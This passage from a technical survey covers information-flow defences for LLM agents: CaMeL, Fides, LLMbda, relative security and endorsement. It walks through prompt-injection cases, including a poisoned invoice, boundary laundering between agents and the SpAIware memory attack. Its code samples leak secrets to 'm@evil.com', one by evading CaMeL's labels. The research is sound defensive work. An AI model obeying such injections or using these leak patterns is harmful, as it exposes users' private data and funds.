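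In the example, the model would very probably propose the same rent payment without the newsletter, so the system generates the proposal again without it, and the monitor allows the payment. If an injection in the newsletter had made the agent propose paying a stranger, that payment would be unlikely without the newsletter, and its label would stay untrusted.

The search in step 2 is only an estimate, and an attacker can skew it. The label is still correct, because the system returns only text that the model wrote without the excluded documents. An injection that changes the first answer can keep the label untrusted and block the user's payment, but it can't insert text into a trusted answer.

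Siddiqui and colleagues tested the search on Llama 2 models. They used 64 questions about invented people. Each question came with 14 separately labeled documents, so there were about 16,000 possible combinations of labels. The search found exactly the right set of labels for 86% of the questions. When the researchers asked the larger model which documents it had used, it was right 13% of the time.

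The search did worse on real prose. A less restrictive label was possible for 647 of 3,465 questions about pairs of trusted and untrusted news articles, and the search found it for 57% of these with the smaller model and 39% with the larger one. It also sometimes left out an untrusted article that the answer needed, which makes the answer worse but not less secure. This happened for 23% of the labels it relaxed with the smaller model and 19% with the larger one.

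With two labels, the system needs one comparison and one rerun per answer, but with many labels the computation required can grow exponentially with the number of documents. Rerunning also can't remove a label when the answer really depends on the labeled document. If the user asks the agent to pay a bill that arrived by e-mail, the payment depends on the e-mail's contents and should keep its label.

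### Measuring influence inside the model

Rerunning treats each document as a whole. *GIF* (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) measures the influence of single tokens or short spans of text, with a method called Geometric Information Flow. In one example, an agent screening job applicants should recommend only those with five years' experience. An unqualified applicant hides an instruction in a CV to recommend them at a salary of $200,000, and the agent obeys. The method attributes 82 bits of influence on the recommendation to the hidden instruction, 27 to the hiring criteria and 16 to everything else.

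The method doesn't remove any words. It uses the model's derivatives to calculate how tiny random changes to a span's embedding would change the probabilities of the next token. The measure is

GIF(τ) = ½ log det(I + τM), where M = JᵀWᵀFWJ

J describes how a small change to the span affects the model's internal state. W converts that state into a score for each possible next token, and F converts changes in the scores into changes in the probabilities. The size of the random changes depends on τ.

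Let U be the random change and Y the next token. Their mutual information, I(U; Y), is the amount that seeing Y reveals about U. Štorek and colleagues proved, in a form that a computer has checked, that

I(U; Y) ≤ GIF(τ) + o(τ) as τ → 0

The last term is an error that shrinks faster than τ, so for sufficiently small changes the measure underestimates influence by at most this error. But an attacker chooses words, and replacing one word with another moves the embedding by a distance that doesn't shrink to zero. Also, when the model is almost certain of the next token, F is close to zero, so every span gets a low score, including the one that made the model certain.

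In practice, the method provides an estimate, which Štorek and colleagues mostly use to rank spans rather than to set a limit in bits. They tested it on six open-weight models with two injection benchmarks, AgentDojo and MSB, and with AgentDAM, which tests whether browsing agents disclose private information.

In the first test, the researchers already knew which tokens were malicious or private, and counted how many of them were among the most influential. This count should be higher for a run in which the agent broke the rules than for a harmless run. With the 50 most influential tokens, the count ranked the two correctly about 91% of the time on AgentDojo, 92% on MSB and 75% on AgentDAM. The figures for an older method based on attention, the weights with which a model combines earlier tokens, were 84%, 76% and 57%.

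A real monitor has no list of malicious tokens, so in the second test another model saw only the one to three most influential spans and decided whether to allow each tool call. With three spans, the small model Qwen 3 8B did as well on the two injection benchmarks as GPT-5.5 did when reading whole runs, at less than an eightieth of the cost. However, the deciding model reads the attacker's text, and the attacks in the benchmarks don't target that model.

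Calculating influence requires the model's weights, which are secret for most commercial models. Štorek and colleagues therefore calculated influence on a 0.6-billion-parameter model to check runs by a 120-billion-parameter one, and detection was almost as good. This is useful for finding attacks, but a bound on the small model's behaviour may not hold for the large one.

### Auditing a finished run

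A third approach looks for taint in the meaning of the agent's actions. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) describes NeuroTaint, which reads the log of a finished run and traces each consequential tool call back to the untrusted sources that influenced it.

NeuroTaint first checks whether the call's arguments contain content from a source. It looks for a unique marker that it attached to the source, then for overlapping text, and then for similar meaning, comparing long documents piece by piece. The check for similar meaning can catch an instruction that the agent has paraphrased.

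A source can influence an agent without leaving such a trace. An e-mail might persuade the agent to forward all of the user's mail, for example, and the forwarded messages would contain none of the e-mail's text. If NeuroTaint finds no shared content, it replaces the source with neutral text such as "No relevant information found" and has a model judge whether the agent would still have made the call. That judgment is only a prediction, whereas Siddiqui and colleagues use an answer that the model wrote without the source.

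Cai and colleagues built a benchmark of 400 scenarios, half of which contain a flow from an untrusted source to a consequential call. NeuroTaint missed 13 of the 200 flows and raised 16 false alarms. Their baseline, based on Fides, missed 92 and raised 106. The baseline treated any path from a source to a consequential tool as strong evidence of influence, so over-tainting explains many of its false alarms. Its misses are less informative because 40 of them come from four of the 20 agent frameworks, on which it raised no alarms. On InjecAgent, an older benchmark of unsafe actions, the two systems did almost equally well.

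NeuroTaint doesn't guarantee that it will catch every flow. In 10 of the 13 flows it missed, repeated paraphrasing or storage in memory had made the text less similar to its source. An attacker could cause this deliberately by asking the agent to reword the text several times. NeuroTaint also audits a run only after it ends, so it can help investigators but can't stop a payment.

### Taint that waits in memory

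A label is lost when a conversation ends unless the system saves it. Cai and colleagues describe an agent that saves a confidential revenue forecast and includes it in a report three days later. Without a saved label, the agent treats the forecast as new and harmless in the second conversation. NeuroTaint avoids this by saving labels alongside the stored text.

A saved label doesn't fully solve the problem, because the planning model has to know what is in memory to use it. *SPA*, from the University of South Florida, gives an example. On Monday, a user asks an agent to find an invoice from Acme and save its details. An attacker has put a false account number and a hidden instruction in the invoice. On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to pay it. If the planning model reads the stored invoice, it also reads the instruction.

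The paper's system, also called SPA, stores every result in three parts:

| Part | What it contains for the invoice | What uses it later |
|---|---|---|
| Value | The text and the account number | Tools and the quarantined model |
| Label | Untrusted | The code that checks plans |
| Description | Its format, its purpose and the request that produced it | The planning model |

The planning model writes the statement of purpose on Monday, before any tool has fetched the invoice, so the statement can't contain the attacker's text. On Tuesday, the planning model sees that the agent has stored details of an Acme invoice and writes a plan to retrieve them and pay it. Retrieving the account number restores its old label. Before any tool runs, SPA follows the labels through the whole plan, finds an untrusted value going into a payment, and rejects the plan. It doesn't let the planning model try again,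 because repeated attempts could eventually produce an unsafe plan that passes.

SPA would also reject the plan if the invoice were genuine. SPA checks the plan before the tools run, so it has to label a new result partly by the tool that will fetch it. A message from a colleague and one from a stranger get the same label if the same tool fetches both.

To test the system, the researchers turned AgentDojo's tasks into series of requests in which later ones need earlier results. They also used the original, single-request tasks:

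| | Single requests | Series of requests |
|---|---|---|
| Attack success rate with label checks | 0.0% | 0.2% |
| Tasks completed without label checks | 53.0% | 62.5% |
| Tasks completed with label checks | 29.0% | 35.3% |

The memory worked well. When a later request needed a stored result and one was available, the agent retrieved it 95.4% of the time without the checks and 89.9% with them. Most of the lost tasks required an action to use outside information, as the invoice payment does.

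### Messages between agents

Many systems now use an orchestrator, an agent that divides a job among specialised agents and calls them like tools. Each specialised agent treats the orchestrator as its user. Peters-Gill and colleagues show that this arrangement can turn untrusted data into trusted instructions, even when every agent runs CaMeL.

In their demonstration, the user asks for a summary of all job applicants to go to Julie on Slack. The orchestrator gets the records from a database agent, has a quarantined model summarise them, and calls a notification agent:

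```python
notification_agent(f"Send this summary to Julie via Slack: {summary}")
```

One database record contains an instruction to send the data to an outside e-mail address. The instruction never reaches the planning models of the orchestrator and the database agent, so their programs don't change. But the notification agent receives the summary as part of its user's request. Its planning model reads the instruction and adds a line to its program that e-mails the applicants' details to the attacker. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering.

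They also prove that this weakness is general. If a system has at least two agents and a tool that returns untrusted data, and users can ask for one tool's result to be used in a call to another tool or agent, then some request will put untrusted data into an agent's instructions. Securing each agent individually still stops attacks that must take over the agent that first reads the hostile text.

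Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, gives each call between agents two channels:

```python
notification_agent(
    message="Send the summary to Julie on Slack.",
    variables={"summary": summary},
)
```

The receiving agent's planning model reads the message but not the variables, which its program can fetch when it runs. The interpreter blocks any message that depends on a tool's output, even a trusted tool's. The variables keep their tags as they pass between agents. Branch steering is still possible, as it is with a single CaMeL agent.

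Peters-Gill and colleagues tested both designs by dividing AgentDojo's tools among several agents. Each percentage is the attack success rate over 949 attacks:

| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

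The difference between the last two columns comes from about nine successful attacks, all of which used boundary laundering on older models. The demonstration and the proof are better reasons to use the second channel than these percentages.

Adding the second channel reduces task completion only slightly once the agents already run CaMeL. On AssetOpsBench, the industrial maintenance benchmark, putting CaMeL in each agent reduced the share of tasks completed by 21.6 percentage points on average, and multi-CaMeL reduced it by another 3.2. For the two strongest models, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, the corresponding reductions were 13.4 points and less than one point. Results on the divided AgentDojo showed a similar pattern, although Fable 5 refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks, perhaps because they resembled a security test.

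All these tests ran without data-flow policies, so they provide no evidence about attack B. If the database supplied a false address for Julie, the orchestrator would pass it on as a variable and the notification agent would use it. The address would keep its tags, so a policy in the notification agent could still check where it came from.

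## Noninterference and the leaks that labels miss

An agent can give away a secret without sending any part of it, because an outsider can learn something from what the agent does or doesn't do. Garby and colleagues give the example of an agent that manages a customer's bank account and runs this code:

```python
if account.balance > threshold:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The e-mail contains only a public word that was already in the program. But whoever receives it learns that the balance is above the threshold, and anyone who expects it and doesn't get it learns that the balance isn't. Security researchers call this an implicit flow, because the information passes through the program's choice of what to do. In an explicit flow, the program sends the secret itself or something computed from it, as in `send_email("m@evil.com", account.balance)`.

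### Two definitions of a leak

In 1982, Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer proposed a definition called noninterference that covers both kinds of flow. SRI, the research institute that developed the theory, explains that one part of a system doesn't interfere with another if nothing the first does can influence what the second later sees.

For a program with a public input x and a secret input s, let O(x, s) be everything that a given observer sees. The program satisfies noninterference if

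O(x, s₁) = O(x, s₂) for all x, s₁ and s₂

One can picture this as running the agent twice, with the same request and incoming mail but different bank balances. If the observer can ever tell the two runs apart, the agent fails. The program above fails for any two balances on opposite sides of the threshold. The definition also works for integrity, with a stranger's text in place of the secret, and requires that changing the text never change a protected action, such as a payment.

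Costa and colleagues considered noninterference too restrictive for Fides. To guarantee it, a monitor would have to forbid nearly every call with visible effects once the agent had made any call that might read a secret. They proved instead that their labelled agent loop can enforce a weaker property, explicit secrecy. Take any series of steps that the agent might carry out, and let g be the combined effect of those steps on the stored data. Let d₁ =_L d₂ mean that two versions of the data differ only in their secrets. Explicit secrecy requires that

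if d₁ =_L d₂, then g(d₁) =_L g(d₂)

Explicit secrecy therefore requires the same steps to produce the same public results whatever the secrets are. Because it holds the steps fixed, it ignores anything an observer could learn from which steps the agent took. The program above puts the word "rich!" in a mailbox when the balance is high and does nothing when it is low. Explicit secrecy accepts both runs because the steps in each would have the same effect with any other balance. It would reject a program that mailed the balance itself.

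The proof also assumes that the model always gives the same output for the same input, and it excludes side channels such as timing and network packet length. TaintDroid and web browsers accept a similar compromise, but it is riskier for an agent because an attacker's text can influence which steps the agent takes. Garby and colleagues point out that explicit secrecy is weakest where data and control are interchangeable, and that leaks through control can be made efficient there.

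### Branching on an answer the attacker controls

An interpreter can catch implicit flows by keeping a label for the point the program has reached, called the program-counter label. When a condition reads a secret, every line inside the branch runs under a secret label. Garby and colleagues say this is why CaMeL refuses to send the "rich!" e-mail. Dongol explains that CaMeL tags values with the conditions that control them only in its strict mode, not in its normal mode.

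Dongol's Tagged Branch example shows how the normal mode can miss a leak. A program asks the quarantined model a question about Alice's private notes and an attacker's e-mail, then sends the attacker a 1 or a 0 depending on the answer. Both numbers are public, so the tag check allows either message. Without an injection, the model's answer would depend only on the e-mail, but an injection can make it depend on the notes. The attacker then learns one fact about the notes, even though the planning model wrote every line of the program and no private value left the system.

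### The assignment that never runs

An interpreter can track conditions and still miss a leak if it updates labels only on the lines that run. J. S. Fenton described the problem in 1974, and Garby and colleagues found it in CaMeL. The leaking program has roughly this form:

```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
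```

When CaMeL runs an assignment inside a branch that depends on a secret, it labels the variable as secret. The labels then develop as follows:

| Program line | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below it |
|---|---|---|
| The first two assignments | `rich` and `tmp` are true and public | `rich` and `tmp` are true and public |
| `if account.balance > threshold` | Sets `tmp` to false and labels it secret | Skips the assignment, so `tmp` stays true and public |
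| `if tmp` | Skips the assignment, so `rich` stays true and public | Sets `rich` to false, still public |
| `if rich` | Sends the e-mail | Sends nothing |

When the balance is high, `if tmp` depends on a secret. CaMeL would have labelled `rich` as secret if it had run the assignment below that line, but it skipped it. `rich` therefore keeps its public label, although its value now reveals whether the balance is above the threshold. The last condition reads only this public variable, so the monitor allows the e-mail.

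An attacker can't write CaMeL's program, and the planning model is unlikely to write this one, so the example is better evidence of a gap in CaMeL's protection than of a practical attack. But the planning model writes a new program for every request, usually with nobody reviewing it, so a guarantee is much more useful if it holds for every program the model might write.

*An Empirical Study of Information Flows in Real-World JavaScript* (2019) describes one of several remedies from research on web scripts, a rule called no-sensitive-upgrade that stops a program when it tries to change a public variable inside a secret branch. Here it would stop the program at `tmp = False`. The rule also stops harmless programs. *Generalizing Permissive-Upgrade in Dynamic Information Flow Analysis* (2015) reports that the compiler in WebKit, a browser engine, adds assignments to variables that the program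 never uses again. If such an assignment falls inside a secret branch, the rule stops the program.

A more permissive rule allows the assignment but stops the program if it later branches on the affected variable. Alternatively, a programmer or an automatic tool can label the variable as secret in both cases by adding a statement before the branch. Adding this statement for `rich` before `if tmp` would block the e-mail in the example.

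### What retries give away

With no-sensitive-upgrade, the program above stops early if the balance is high and finishes if it is low, so anyone who can see whether it finished still learns whether the balance is high. Most information-flow systems tolerate this leak because a single run reveals little. Researchers call a guarantee that ignores this leak termination-insensitive.

CaMeL's retry loop makes the leak larger because every new program starts without tags, so each attempt can reveal the answer to a different yes-or-no question about the secret. If each answer halves the remaining possibilities, 20 attempts are enough to find a balance below £1 million to the nearest pound.

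A designer can close this channel by applying the same labels to the retry loop as to everything else. Garby and colleagues did this for their own agent, so it does trial runs on invented data before it accesses the real account.

### What LLMbda proves

Garby and colleagues wrote that agent in LLMbda, a small programming language based on the lambda calculus, a minimal mathematical language of functions. In LLMbda, every value and every conversation with a model has a label. A program can clear a conversation, or fork it so that later messages don't affect the original. Developers can therefore create a quarantined model when they need one by forking and clearing a conversation, instead of building the separation into the system.

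If the model replies with code, LLMbda runs the code under the label of the conversation that produced it. Code from an untrusted conversation can therefore produce only untrusted results.

LLMbda applies a version of no-sensitive-upgrade to conversations. In one example, a program tells the model to remember that x is false. If a secret is true, the program then tells the model to set x to true. In either case, it ends by asking for x. LLMbda stops the program when it tries to send the second message. Relabelling the conversation as secret wouldn't prevent the leak, because if the secret were false, the program would never send that message and the conversation would stay public.

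The main theorem is a form of noninterference that holds for every program in LLMbda, including agents that write and run code. Because a model's replies are partly random, the theorem is about the probabilities of what an observer sees. If a program always finishes, these probabilities must be exactly the same whatever the secrets are.

For programs that may not finish, let μ(q) and ν(q) be the probabilities that two runs, differing only in their secrets, finish with a result q that the observer can distinguish from others. The theorem guarantees that some third set of probabilities, ω, satisfies

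μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, with Σ ω(q) ≤ 1

This means that the unfinished runs could account for the whole difference between μ and ν. Suppose, for instance, that an agent answers "yes" or "no":

| | "Yes" | "No" | Doesn't finish |
|---|---|---|---|
| With one secret (μ) | 0.6 | 0.3 | 0.1 |
| With another secret (ν) | 0.5 | 0.4 | 0.1 |
| Smallest possible ω | 0.6 | 0.4 | |

The smallest ω adds up to 1, so this agent passes. If the second secret gave "yes" a probability of 0.4 and "no" 0.5, ω would have to add up to at least 1.1, and the agent would fail. Garby and colleagues also prove that the leak, measured as half the sum of the differences between μ and ν, is never more than the average probability of not finishing. Both numbers are 0.1 in the table. An agent that nearly always finishes can therefore leak very little this way in one run.

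The proof of the theorem uses a second way to run a program, which skips any computation too secret for the observer and substitutes an empty value. The results of this version can't depend on the secret, and it finishes at least as often as the original, so its probabilities can serve as ω for both runs.

Lean, a proof assistant, checked the whole argument. It also checked that the interpreter follows the mathematical definition of the language, so the theorems apply to the software that calls the model. Their only assumption about the model is that its replies follow fixed probabilities for any given conversation, not that it behaves well.

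Developers still have to label their data correctly and put checks on sensitive tools. The theory also treats every data source as part of the program, and Garby and colleagues acknowledge that a better model would cover general exchanges with outside tools. Readers can easily overlook such limits when a system is described as machine-checked. *PerMIT* (2026), a design for protecting an agent's stored memory, also has an integrity theorem in Lean, but the proof covers a single-user interpreter, not the protocol for sharing memory between users.

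### An assistant that has to disclose something

Noninterference forbids many useful agents. Dongol's calendar assistant, which may send Alice's calendar to anyone who requests a meeting, violates noninterference whenever it sends the calendar, because two runs with the same meeting request but different calendars give the requester different replies. The assistant also violates explicit secrecy, because it copies the calendar directly into its reply.

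A developer could write a policy that permits this release, but every task would need its own. Each policy would describe what the agent may disclose, not what an injection has added.

In November 2026, Dongol proposed judging agents by relative security instead. This compares the agent with a reference agent that has the same plan and monitor but whose model never obeys untrusted content. The idea comes from research on processors that save time by guessing which instructions come next and running them early. Attacks such as Spectre extract secrets from the effects of wrong guesses. To judge a program on such a processor, researchers compare it with the same program run strictly in order and count only the additional leaks as violations.

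For agents, a leak is a pair of runs in which the attacker supplies the same content and the secrets differ, and in which the attacker sees different things. If the secrets in the two runs are σ₁ and σ₂, relative security requires that

if the agent leaks (σ₁, σ₂), then its twin also leaks (σ₁, σ₂)

The twin must start with the same memory and trusted inputs, but the attacker may send it different content. The calendar assistant therefore satisfies relative security even if it obeys an injected order to send the calendar, because the twin would reveal the same calendar in response to a genuine request. The assistant violates relative security if the injection also extracts the private reset code, because no e-mail would make the twin send the code.

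| Case | Noninterference | Explicit secrecy | Relative security |
|---|---|---|---|
| The assistant discloses the calendar | Rejects | Rejects | Accepts |
| An injection discloses the reset code | Rejects | Rejects | Rejects |
| Tagged Branch discloses a fact about the notes | Rejects | Accepts | Rejects |

An agent can also satisfy relative security and still have a serious leak. Suppose its task is to tell a sender whether they have guessed a four-digit PIN correctly. For any two PINs, some guess would distinguish them, so the twin already leaks every pair. An injection that makes the agent send the whole PIN then adds no new pair, although without it the attacker might have needed thousands of guesses. Dongol therefore defines a stricter version, uniform relative security, in which what the attacker sends to the twin can't depend on the secrets.

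Attack B on the meeting notes also passes. If an attacker replaces Bob's address with their own, a model that never obeys injected instructions will still read the false address, and the twin will send the attacker the document. Relative security doesn't count this leak against the agent, because ignoring injected instructions wouldn't have prevented it.

### Where to put the fence

Dongol's Leaky Summariser is an agent that fails the comparison. Alice asks for a summary of an e-mail. The agent looks up her private account number, reads the e-mail and shows her the summary. It also has a tool for fetching web pages, which the task doesn't need. The attacker's e-mail contains instructions to fetch a page on the attacker's site and put the account number in the web address. If the model follows them, the attacker receives the number, whereas the twin never fetches anything. Removing either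 the inbox or the web tool would prevent the leak.

In the Fenced Summariser, the monitor revokes the web tool as soon as the agent reads the e-mail. Dongol calls this a fence. The model can still request the page, but the monitor blocks the request without the attacker noticing, and Alice gets her summary.

The position of the fence matters. On a processor, a barrier can go just before the existing instruction that would leak. An injection adds its own call, which the model may make at any time after reading it. Dongol compares three agents whose plans include a step that locks the tool for sending messages:

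| Agent | Order of steps | What an injected message could contain |
|---|---|---|
| Late Fence | Read the e-mail, read a secret, lock | The secret |
| Middle Fence | Read the e-mail, lock, read a secret | Private data already in memory, perhaps from an earlier session |
| Early Fence | Lock before reading the e-mail | Nothing, because the monitor refuses to send it |

The fence theorem extends this result to every plan. It states that an agent is relatively secure if, at the first untrusted read, the monitor permanently revokes every tool an injection could call. The proof matches each run of the agent with a run of its twin. Whenever the agent makes an injected call, the monitor silently refuses it and the twin waits. Otherwise the two take the same steps, so the attacker sees the same messages from both. The same argument proves the stricter, uniform version. Dongol produced the proofs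 with the help of Claude Code, and the proof assistant Isabelle checked them.

In practice, this fence works like the trusted action policy in Fides when one label covers the whole conversation, and it has the same drawback. If the task requires a reply after the agent has read the e-mail, a fence around the sending tool blocks that reply too. This loss doesn't violate relative security, because the twin loses the tool as well. Even an agent whose monitor refused every call would satisfy relative security. In the GitHub attack, a fence would have kept the private data out of the public pull request, but it would also have blocked any pull request that the user wanted.

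### What the fence theorem assumes

The theorem makes no assumption about which texts the model treats as instructions, but it does require the following:

- A trusted planner fixes the plan before the agent reads anything untrusted, and ordinary code carries it out.
- The model can reach tools and untrusted sources only through the monitor.
- Each injection causes a single call, to one of the tools that the fence revokes.
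- The timing of the model's obedience doesn't depend on secrets or on the monitor's replies.
- The attacker sees the content and order of the agent's messages, but not their timing or the monitor's refusals.
- The run eventually ends.

Some of these conditions can be relaxed. If an injection can run a whole program rather than a single call, the program might overwrite a variable that the plan later sends. In Dongol's example, an agent returns an attacker's e-mail to its sender. The injected program overwrites the stored e-mail with a secret, and the agent then sends the secret in a call that was already in the plan. In this case, a fence is enough only if it also covers reads and the injected program runs in a sandbox that discards its changes.

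An agent that handles e-mails indefinitely needs its tools restored for each new one. Restoring them is safe if the agent first starts a fresh session, with no earlier e-mails in the model's context, and if the model doesn't keep obeying injections forever.

A session isn't fresh if it loads memory that an attacker has written. In SpAIware, an attack on ChatGPT reported in 2024, a document caused the assistant to save an instruction in its long-term memory. The instruction was loaded into later conversations and made the assistant display images whose web addresses contained the user's messages. Dongol's model of the attack shows that a fence can stop it, provided the monitor treats loading the memory as an untrusted read.

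A visible refusal can leak information even when the monitor correctly blocks a call. For example, if a private setting determines whether an agent may use an internal tool and an injection makes the model try it, an attacker who can see the error message learns the setting. Timing can also leak information, but the theorem extends to an attacker who can time the agent's messages if the plan's branches don't depend on secrets.

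Relative security concerns only leaks, so it doesn't cover an injection that deletes files without disclosing anything. Dongol also excludes side channels, multi-agent systems, mistakes by the planner, and any tool whose reply depends on the request, such as a search engine that the attacker operates.

The largest excluded group is agents whose model chooses each tool call as it goes, because they have no fixed plan for a twin to follow. This group includes the ordinary agent loop and Fides.

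## Letting chosen untrusted data through: endorsement, declassification and approval

A monitor that always kept untrusted data out of actions and private data away from outsiders would block some tasks that users want done. Paying a bill means letting a stranger's text determine a payment, and answering a customer may mean sending private information outside the account. Askarov and Myers (2011), in *Attacker Control and Impact for Confidentiality and Integrity*, called this strict separation, known as noninterference, too inflexible for realistic applications. Languages that track information flow have long included ways to make exceptions.

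### Two kinds of exception

Endorsement means deliberately treating an untrusted value as trusted for a stated use. Declassification means deliberately releasing confidential data to someone who couldn't otherwise read it. *Nonmalleable Information Flow* (2017) calls both downgrading, because each lets information flow where its labels would normally forbid it. The request to send Bob his document may need both. If the policy requires a trusted recipient, someone has to endorse the address in the meeting notes, and if Bob isn't yet allowed to read the document, someone has to declassify it.

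Endorsing Bob's address only records that somebody has accepted the risk of using it, without checking that the address is Bob's. The system's security therefore depends on who can cause an exception and how much can pass through it.

Suppose a shop may print any four digits of a customer's 16-digit card number on a receipt. An attacker who can choose the digits needs only four receipts to learn the whole number. The shop has limited what each receipt reveals, but not who chooses the digits. Robust declassification adds that second limit by allowing a release only if untrusted data influenced neither the decision to release nor what was released. *Demystifying Information Flow Downgrading using the Real–Ideal Paradigm* (2026) describes it as a requirement that an attacker who interferes with the program learn no more than one who only watches.

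Let O(s, a) be everything the attacker sees when the secret is s and the attacker supplies the input a. A program is robust if, for all secrets s₁ and s₂ and all inputs a and a′,

if O(s₁, a) = O(s₂, a), then O(s₁, a′) = O(s₂, a′)

A program that multiplies the attacker's number by a secret number and publishes the result fails this test. An attacker who supplies 0 learns nothing, but one who supplies 1 learns the secret.

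Costa and colleagues point out that the trusted action policy alone can give an agent a form of robust declassification, because under that policy private data can reach a new reader only while the conversation is trusted. Microsoft describes its policy for posting in Teams in the same terms. If Alex tells the agent to send the sales preview to Marco, the agent sends it unless it has already read Marco's e-mail. In that case, the monitor asks Alex to approve the message, since the e-mail may have prompted it.

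Some useful agents fail the test of robust declassification. Dongol gives the example of an assistant that sends Alice's calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. It sends the calendar in response to a meeting request but not a newsletter, so the sender's text determines whether the calendar is released. To pass, the assistant must endorse the answer to "Is this a meeting request?", and that one answer then permits the release of the whole calendar.

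Endorsement can also go wrong when the person who supplied a value couldn't have read it. Suppose a quarantined model reads a stranger's e-mail together with the user's private notes. The e-mail could make the model copy a line from the notes into its answer. A program that then endorsed the answer as the stranger's choice would be wrong to do so, because the answer would include text the stranger couldn't have read. *Nonmalleable Information Flow* rules this out with a condition called transparent endorsement, which lets a program endorse only information that its provider could have read.

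### Limits by size

A yes-or-no answer seems safer to endorse than a paragraph because it cannot contain an instruction. Costa and colleagues apply this idea in Fides, whose labels can record a value's type as well as its integrity and permitted readers. A value with n possible settings carries at most log₂ n bits of information, so a yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit and a choice among eight options at most three, while free text has no fixed limit. A policy could let an untrusted yes-or-no answer influence a consequential tool call while still refusing untrusted free text.

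In an example from Costa and colleagues, a user asks the agent to check three e-mails for a meeting request and to create a calendar event if it finds one. A quarantined model returns yes or no, and the planning model reads the result. If the result is yes, the quarantined model extracts the date, time and guests into a variable, which the planning model passes to the calendar without reading its contents. Costa and colleagues consider a Boolean (true or false) value "unlikely" to lead to a prompt injection, so they suggest a policy that allows the event.

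One bit can't tell the planning model to do something new, but it can trigger an expensive action that the user has already requested. If the user asks the agent to pay a builder £5,000 once the builder confirms that the roof is finished, a single false "yes" costs the user £5,000. The number of bits limits how many outcomes an attacker can choose between, not how bad they are. Choosing one of eight recipients takes three bits whether all eight are colleagues or one is the attacker. In the first case, Bob's document could go to the wrong colleague, while in the second it could go to the attacker. Even an eight-digit account number carries fewer than 27 bits, and a thief who can choose that number can direct a payment to their own account.

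Small answers also add up, as they do in CaMeL's retry loop. If a program asks k questions with n possible answers each, an attacker who controls the answers controls up to

k log₂ n bits

The type in a Fides label doesn't show how many yes-or-no questions have been asked, because joining two yes-or-no labels gives another yes-or-no label. Foerster and colleagues limit repeated questions in their screen agent for a similar reason.

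Costa and colleagues left constrained answers out of the Fides planner they tested on AgentDojo, because most of the benchmark's tasks didn't need them. The results therefore don't show how many more tasks the agent could complete with constrained answers, or how well those answers would resist an attack.

A program that enforces a size limit also has to do its steps in the right order. Garby and colleagues describe an agent that sorts incoming e-mail and uses the category as the subject of its reply, which must be trusted. The quarantined model's answer is untrusted, so the program endorses it if it is on a fixed list. In Python-like form, the obvious way to write this is:

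```python
if answer in ["invoice", "complaint", "general"]:
    subject = endorse(answer)      # still untrusted
```

This has no effect in LLMbda, their language for agents. The condition reads an untrusted value, so everything computed inside the branch is untrusted too, including the result of the endorsement. The program has to endorse a copy first and use it only if it passes the test:

```python
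copy = endorse(answer)
subject = copy if copy in ["invoice", "complaint", "general"] else answer
```

An answer that isn't on the list keeps its untrusted label, and the mail tool rejects it. Garby and colleagues haven't yet proved a limit in bits for this construction.

The rule that makes the first version useless also protects against injected endorsements. If an attacker's text became code that contained its own endorsements, that code would run as untrusted and the endorsements would have no effect. The protection fails if an earlier step has already endorsed the attacker's text. Garby and colleagues suggest permanently marking every endorsed value and refusing to endorse it, or anything computed from it, a second time.

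### An agent that names its exceptions in advance

Randori, the agent that Garby and colleagues built in LLMbda, decides on its endorsements before it reads any real data. The name is a martial arts term for free sparring, after the rehearsal that each task begins with:

1. The planning model receives the request, the tool descriptions and the rules about which arguments must be trusted.
2. It writes a program and tries it on an invented bank account. Reading a file returns a fixed placeholder, and payments change nothing.
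3. If the program fails, the model sees the error and tries again. The errors can't carry an attacker's text, because all the data is invented.
4. The model writes a final program, which can include endorsements.
5. The final program runs on the real account, and the model can't revise it.

For a bill in a file, the final program might look like this in simplified form:

```python
bill = read_file("bill.txt")
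payee = endorse(ask_quarantined("Which account should be paid?", bill))
amount = endorse(ask_quarantined("How much is due?", bill))
send_money(payee, amount)
```

In LLMbda, a reviewer can find every exception by searching the program for `endorse`. Garby and colleagues consider this an advantage over Fides, where a policy may accept an untrusted value because of its type, and nobody can tell from a given run whether that was intended or a leak. LLMbda's theorems also guarantee that endorsing a value never makes a secret public. But they don't limit how much the planning model may endorse, so it could endorse everything.

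Garby and colleagues tested Randori on AgentDojo's banking suite and reran CaMeL for comparison. They ran each of the 16 tasks without an attack and each of the 144 task-attack pairs, all three times. They reported results separately for the 97 pairs in which planning before reading should stop the attack and the other 47, in which the user's own program could serve the attacker.

| Agent | Model | Tasks completed, no attack | Successful attacks, 97 pairs | Successful attacks, 47 pairs |
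|---|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 75.0% | 0 of 291 | 2 of 141 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 75.0% | 0 of 291 | 0 of 141 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 64.6% | 0 of 291 | 0 of 141 |
| Randori, no endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 62.5% | 0 of 291 | 0 of 141 |
| Randori, no endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 54.2% | 0 of 291 | 0 of 141 |
| CaMeL, no policies | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 1 of 99 | 0 of 141 |
| CaMeL, no policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 1 of 241 | 3 of 141 |
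| CaMeL, with policies | GPT-5.2 | 37.5% | 0 of 97 | 0 of 134 |
| CaMeL, with policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 37.5% | 0 of 216 | 0 of 141 |

With endorsement available, Randori let through two of 1,296 attacks and completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did without policies. With its policies on, CaMeL completed roughly half as many. Some of CaMeL's attacked runs didn't finish, so its attack totals are smaller.

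With only 16 tasks, the percentages are imprecise. With GPT-5.2, the 95% confidence intervals are 75% ± 19 points for Randori, 67% ± 23 for CaMeL without policies and 38% ± 27 for CaMeL with policies. The difference between the first two could easily be due to chance.

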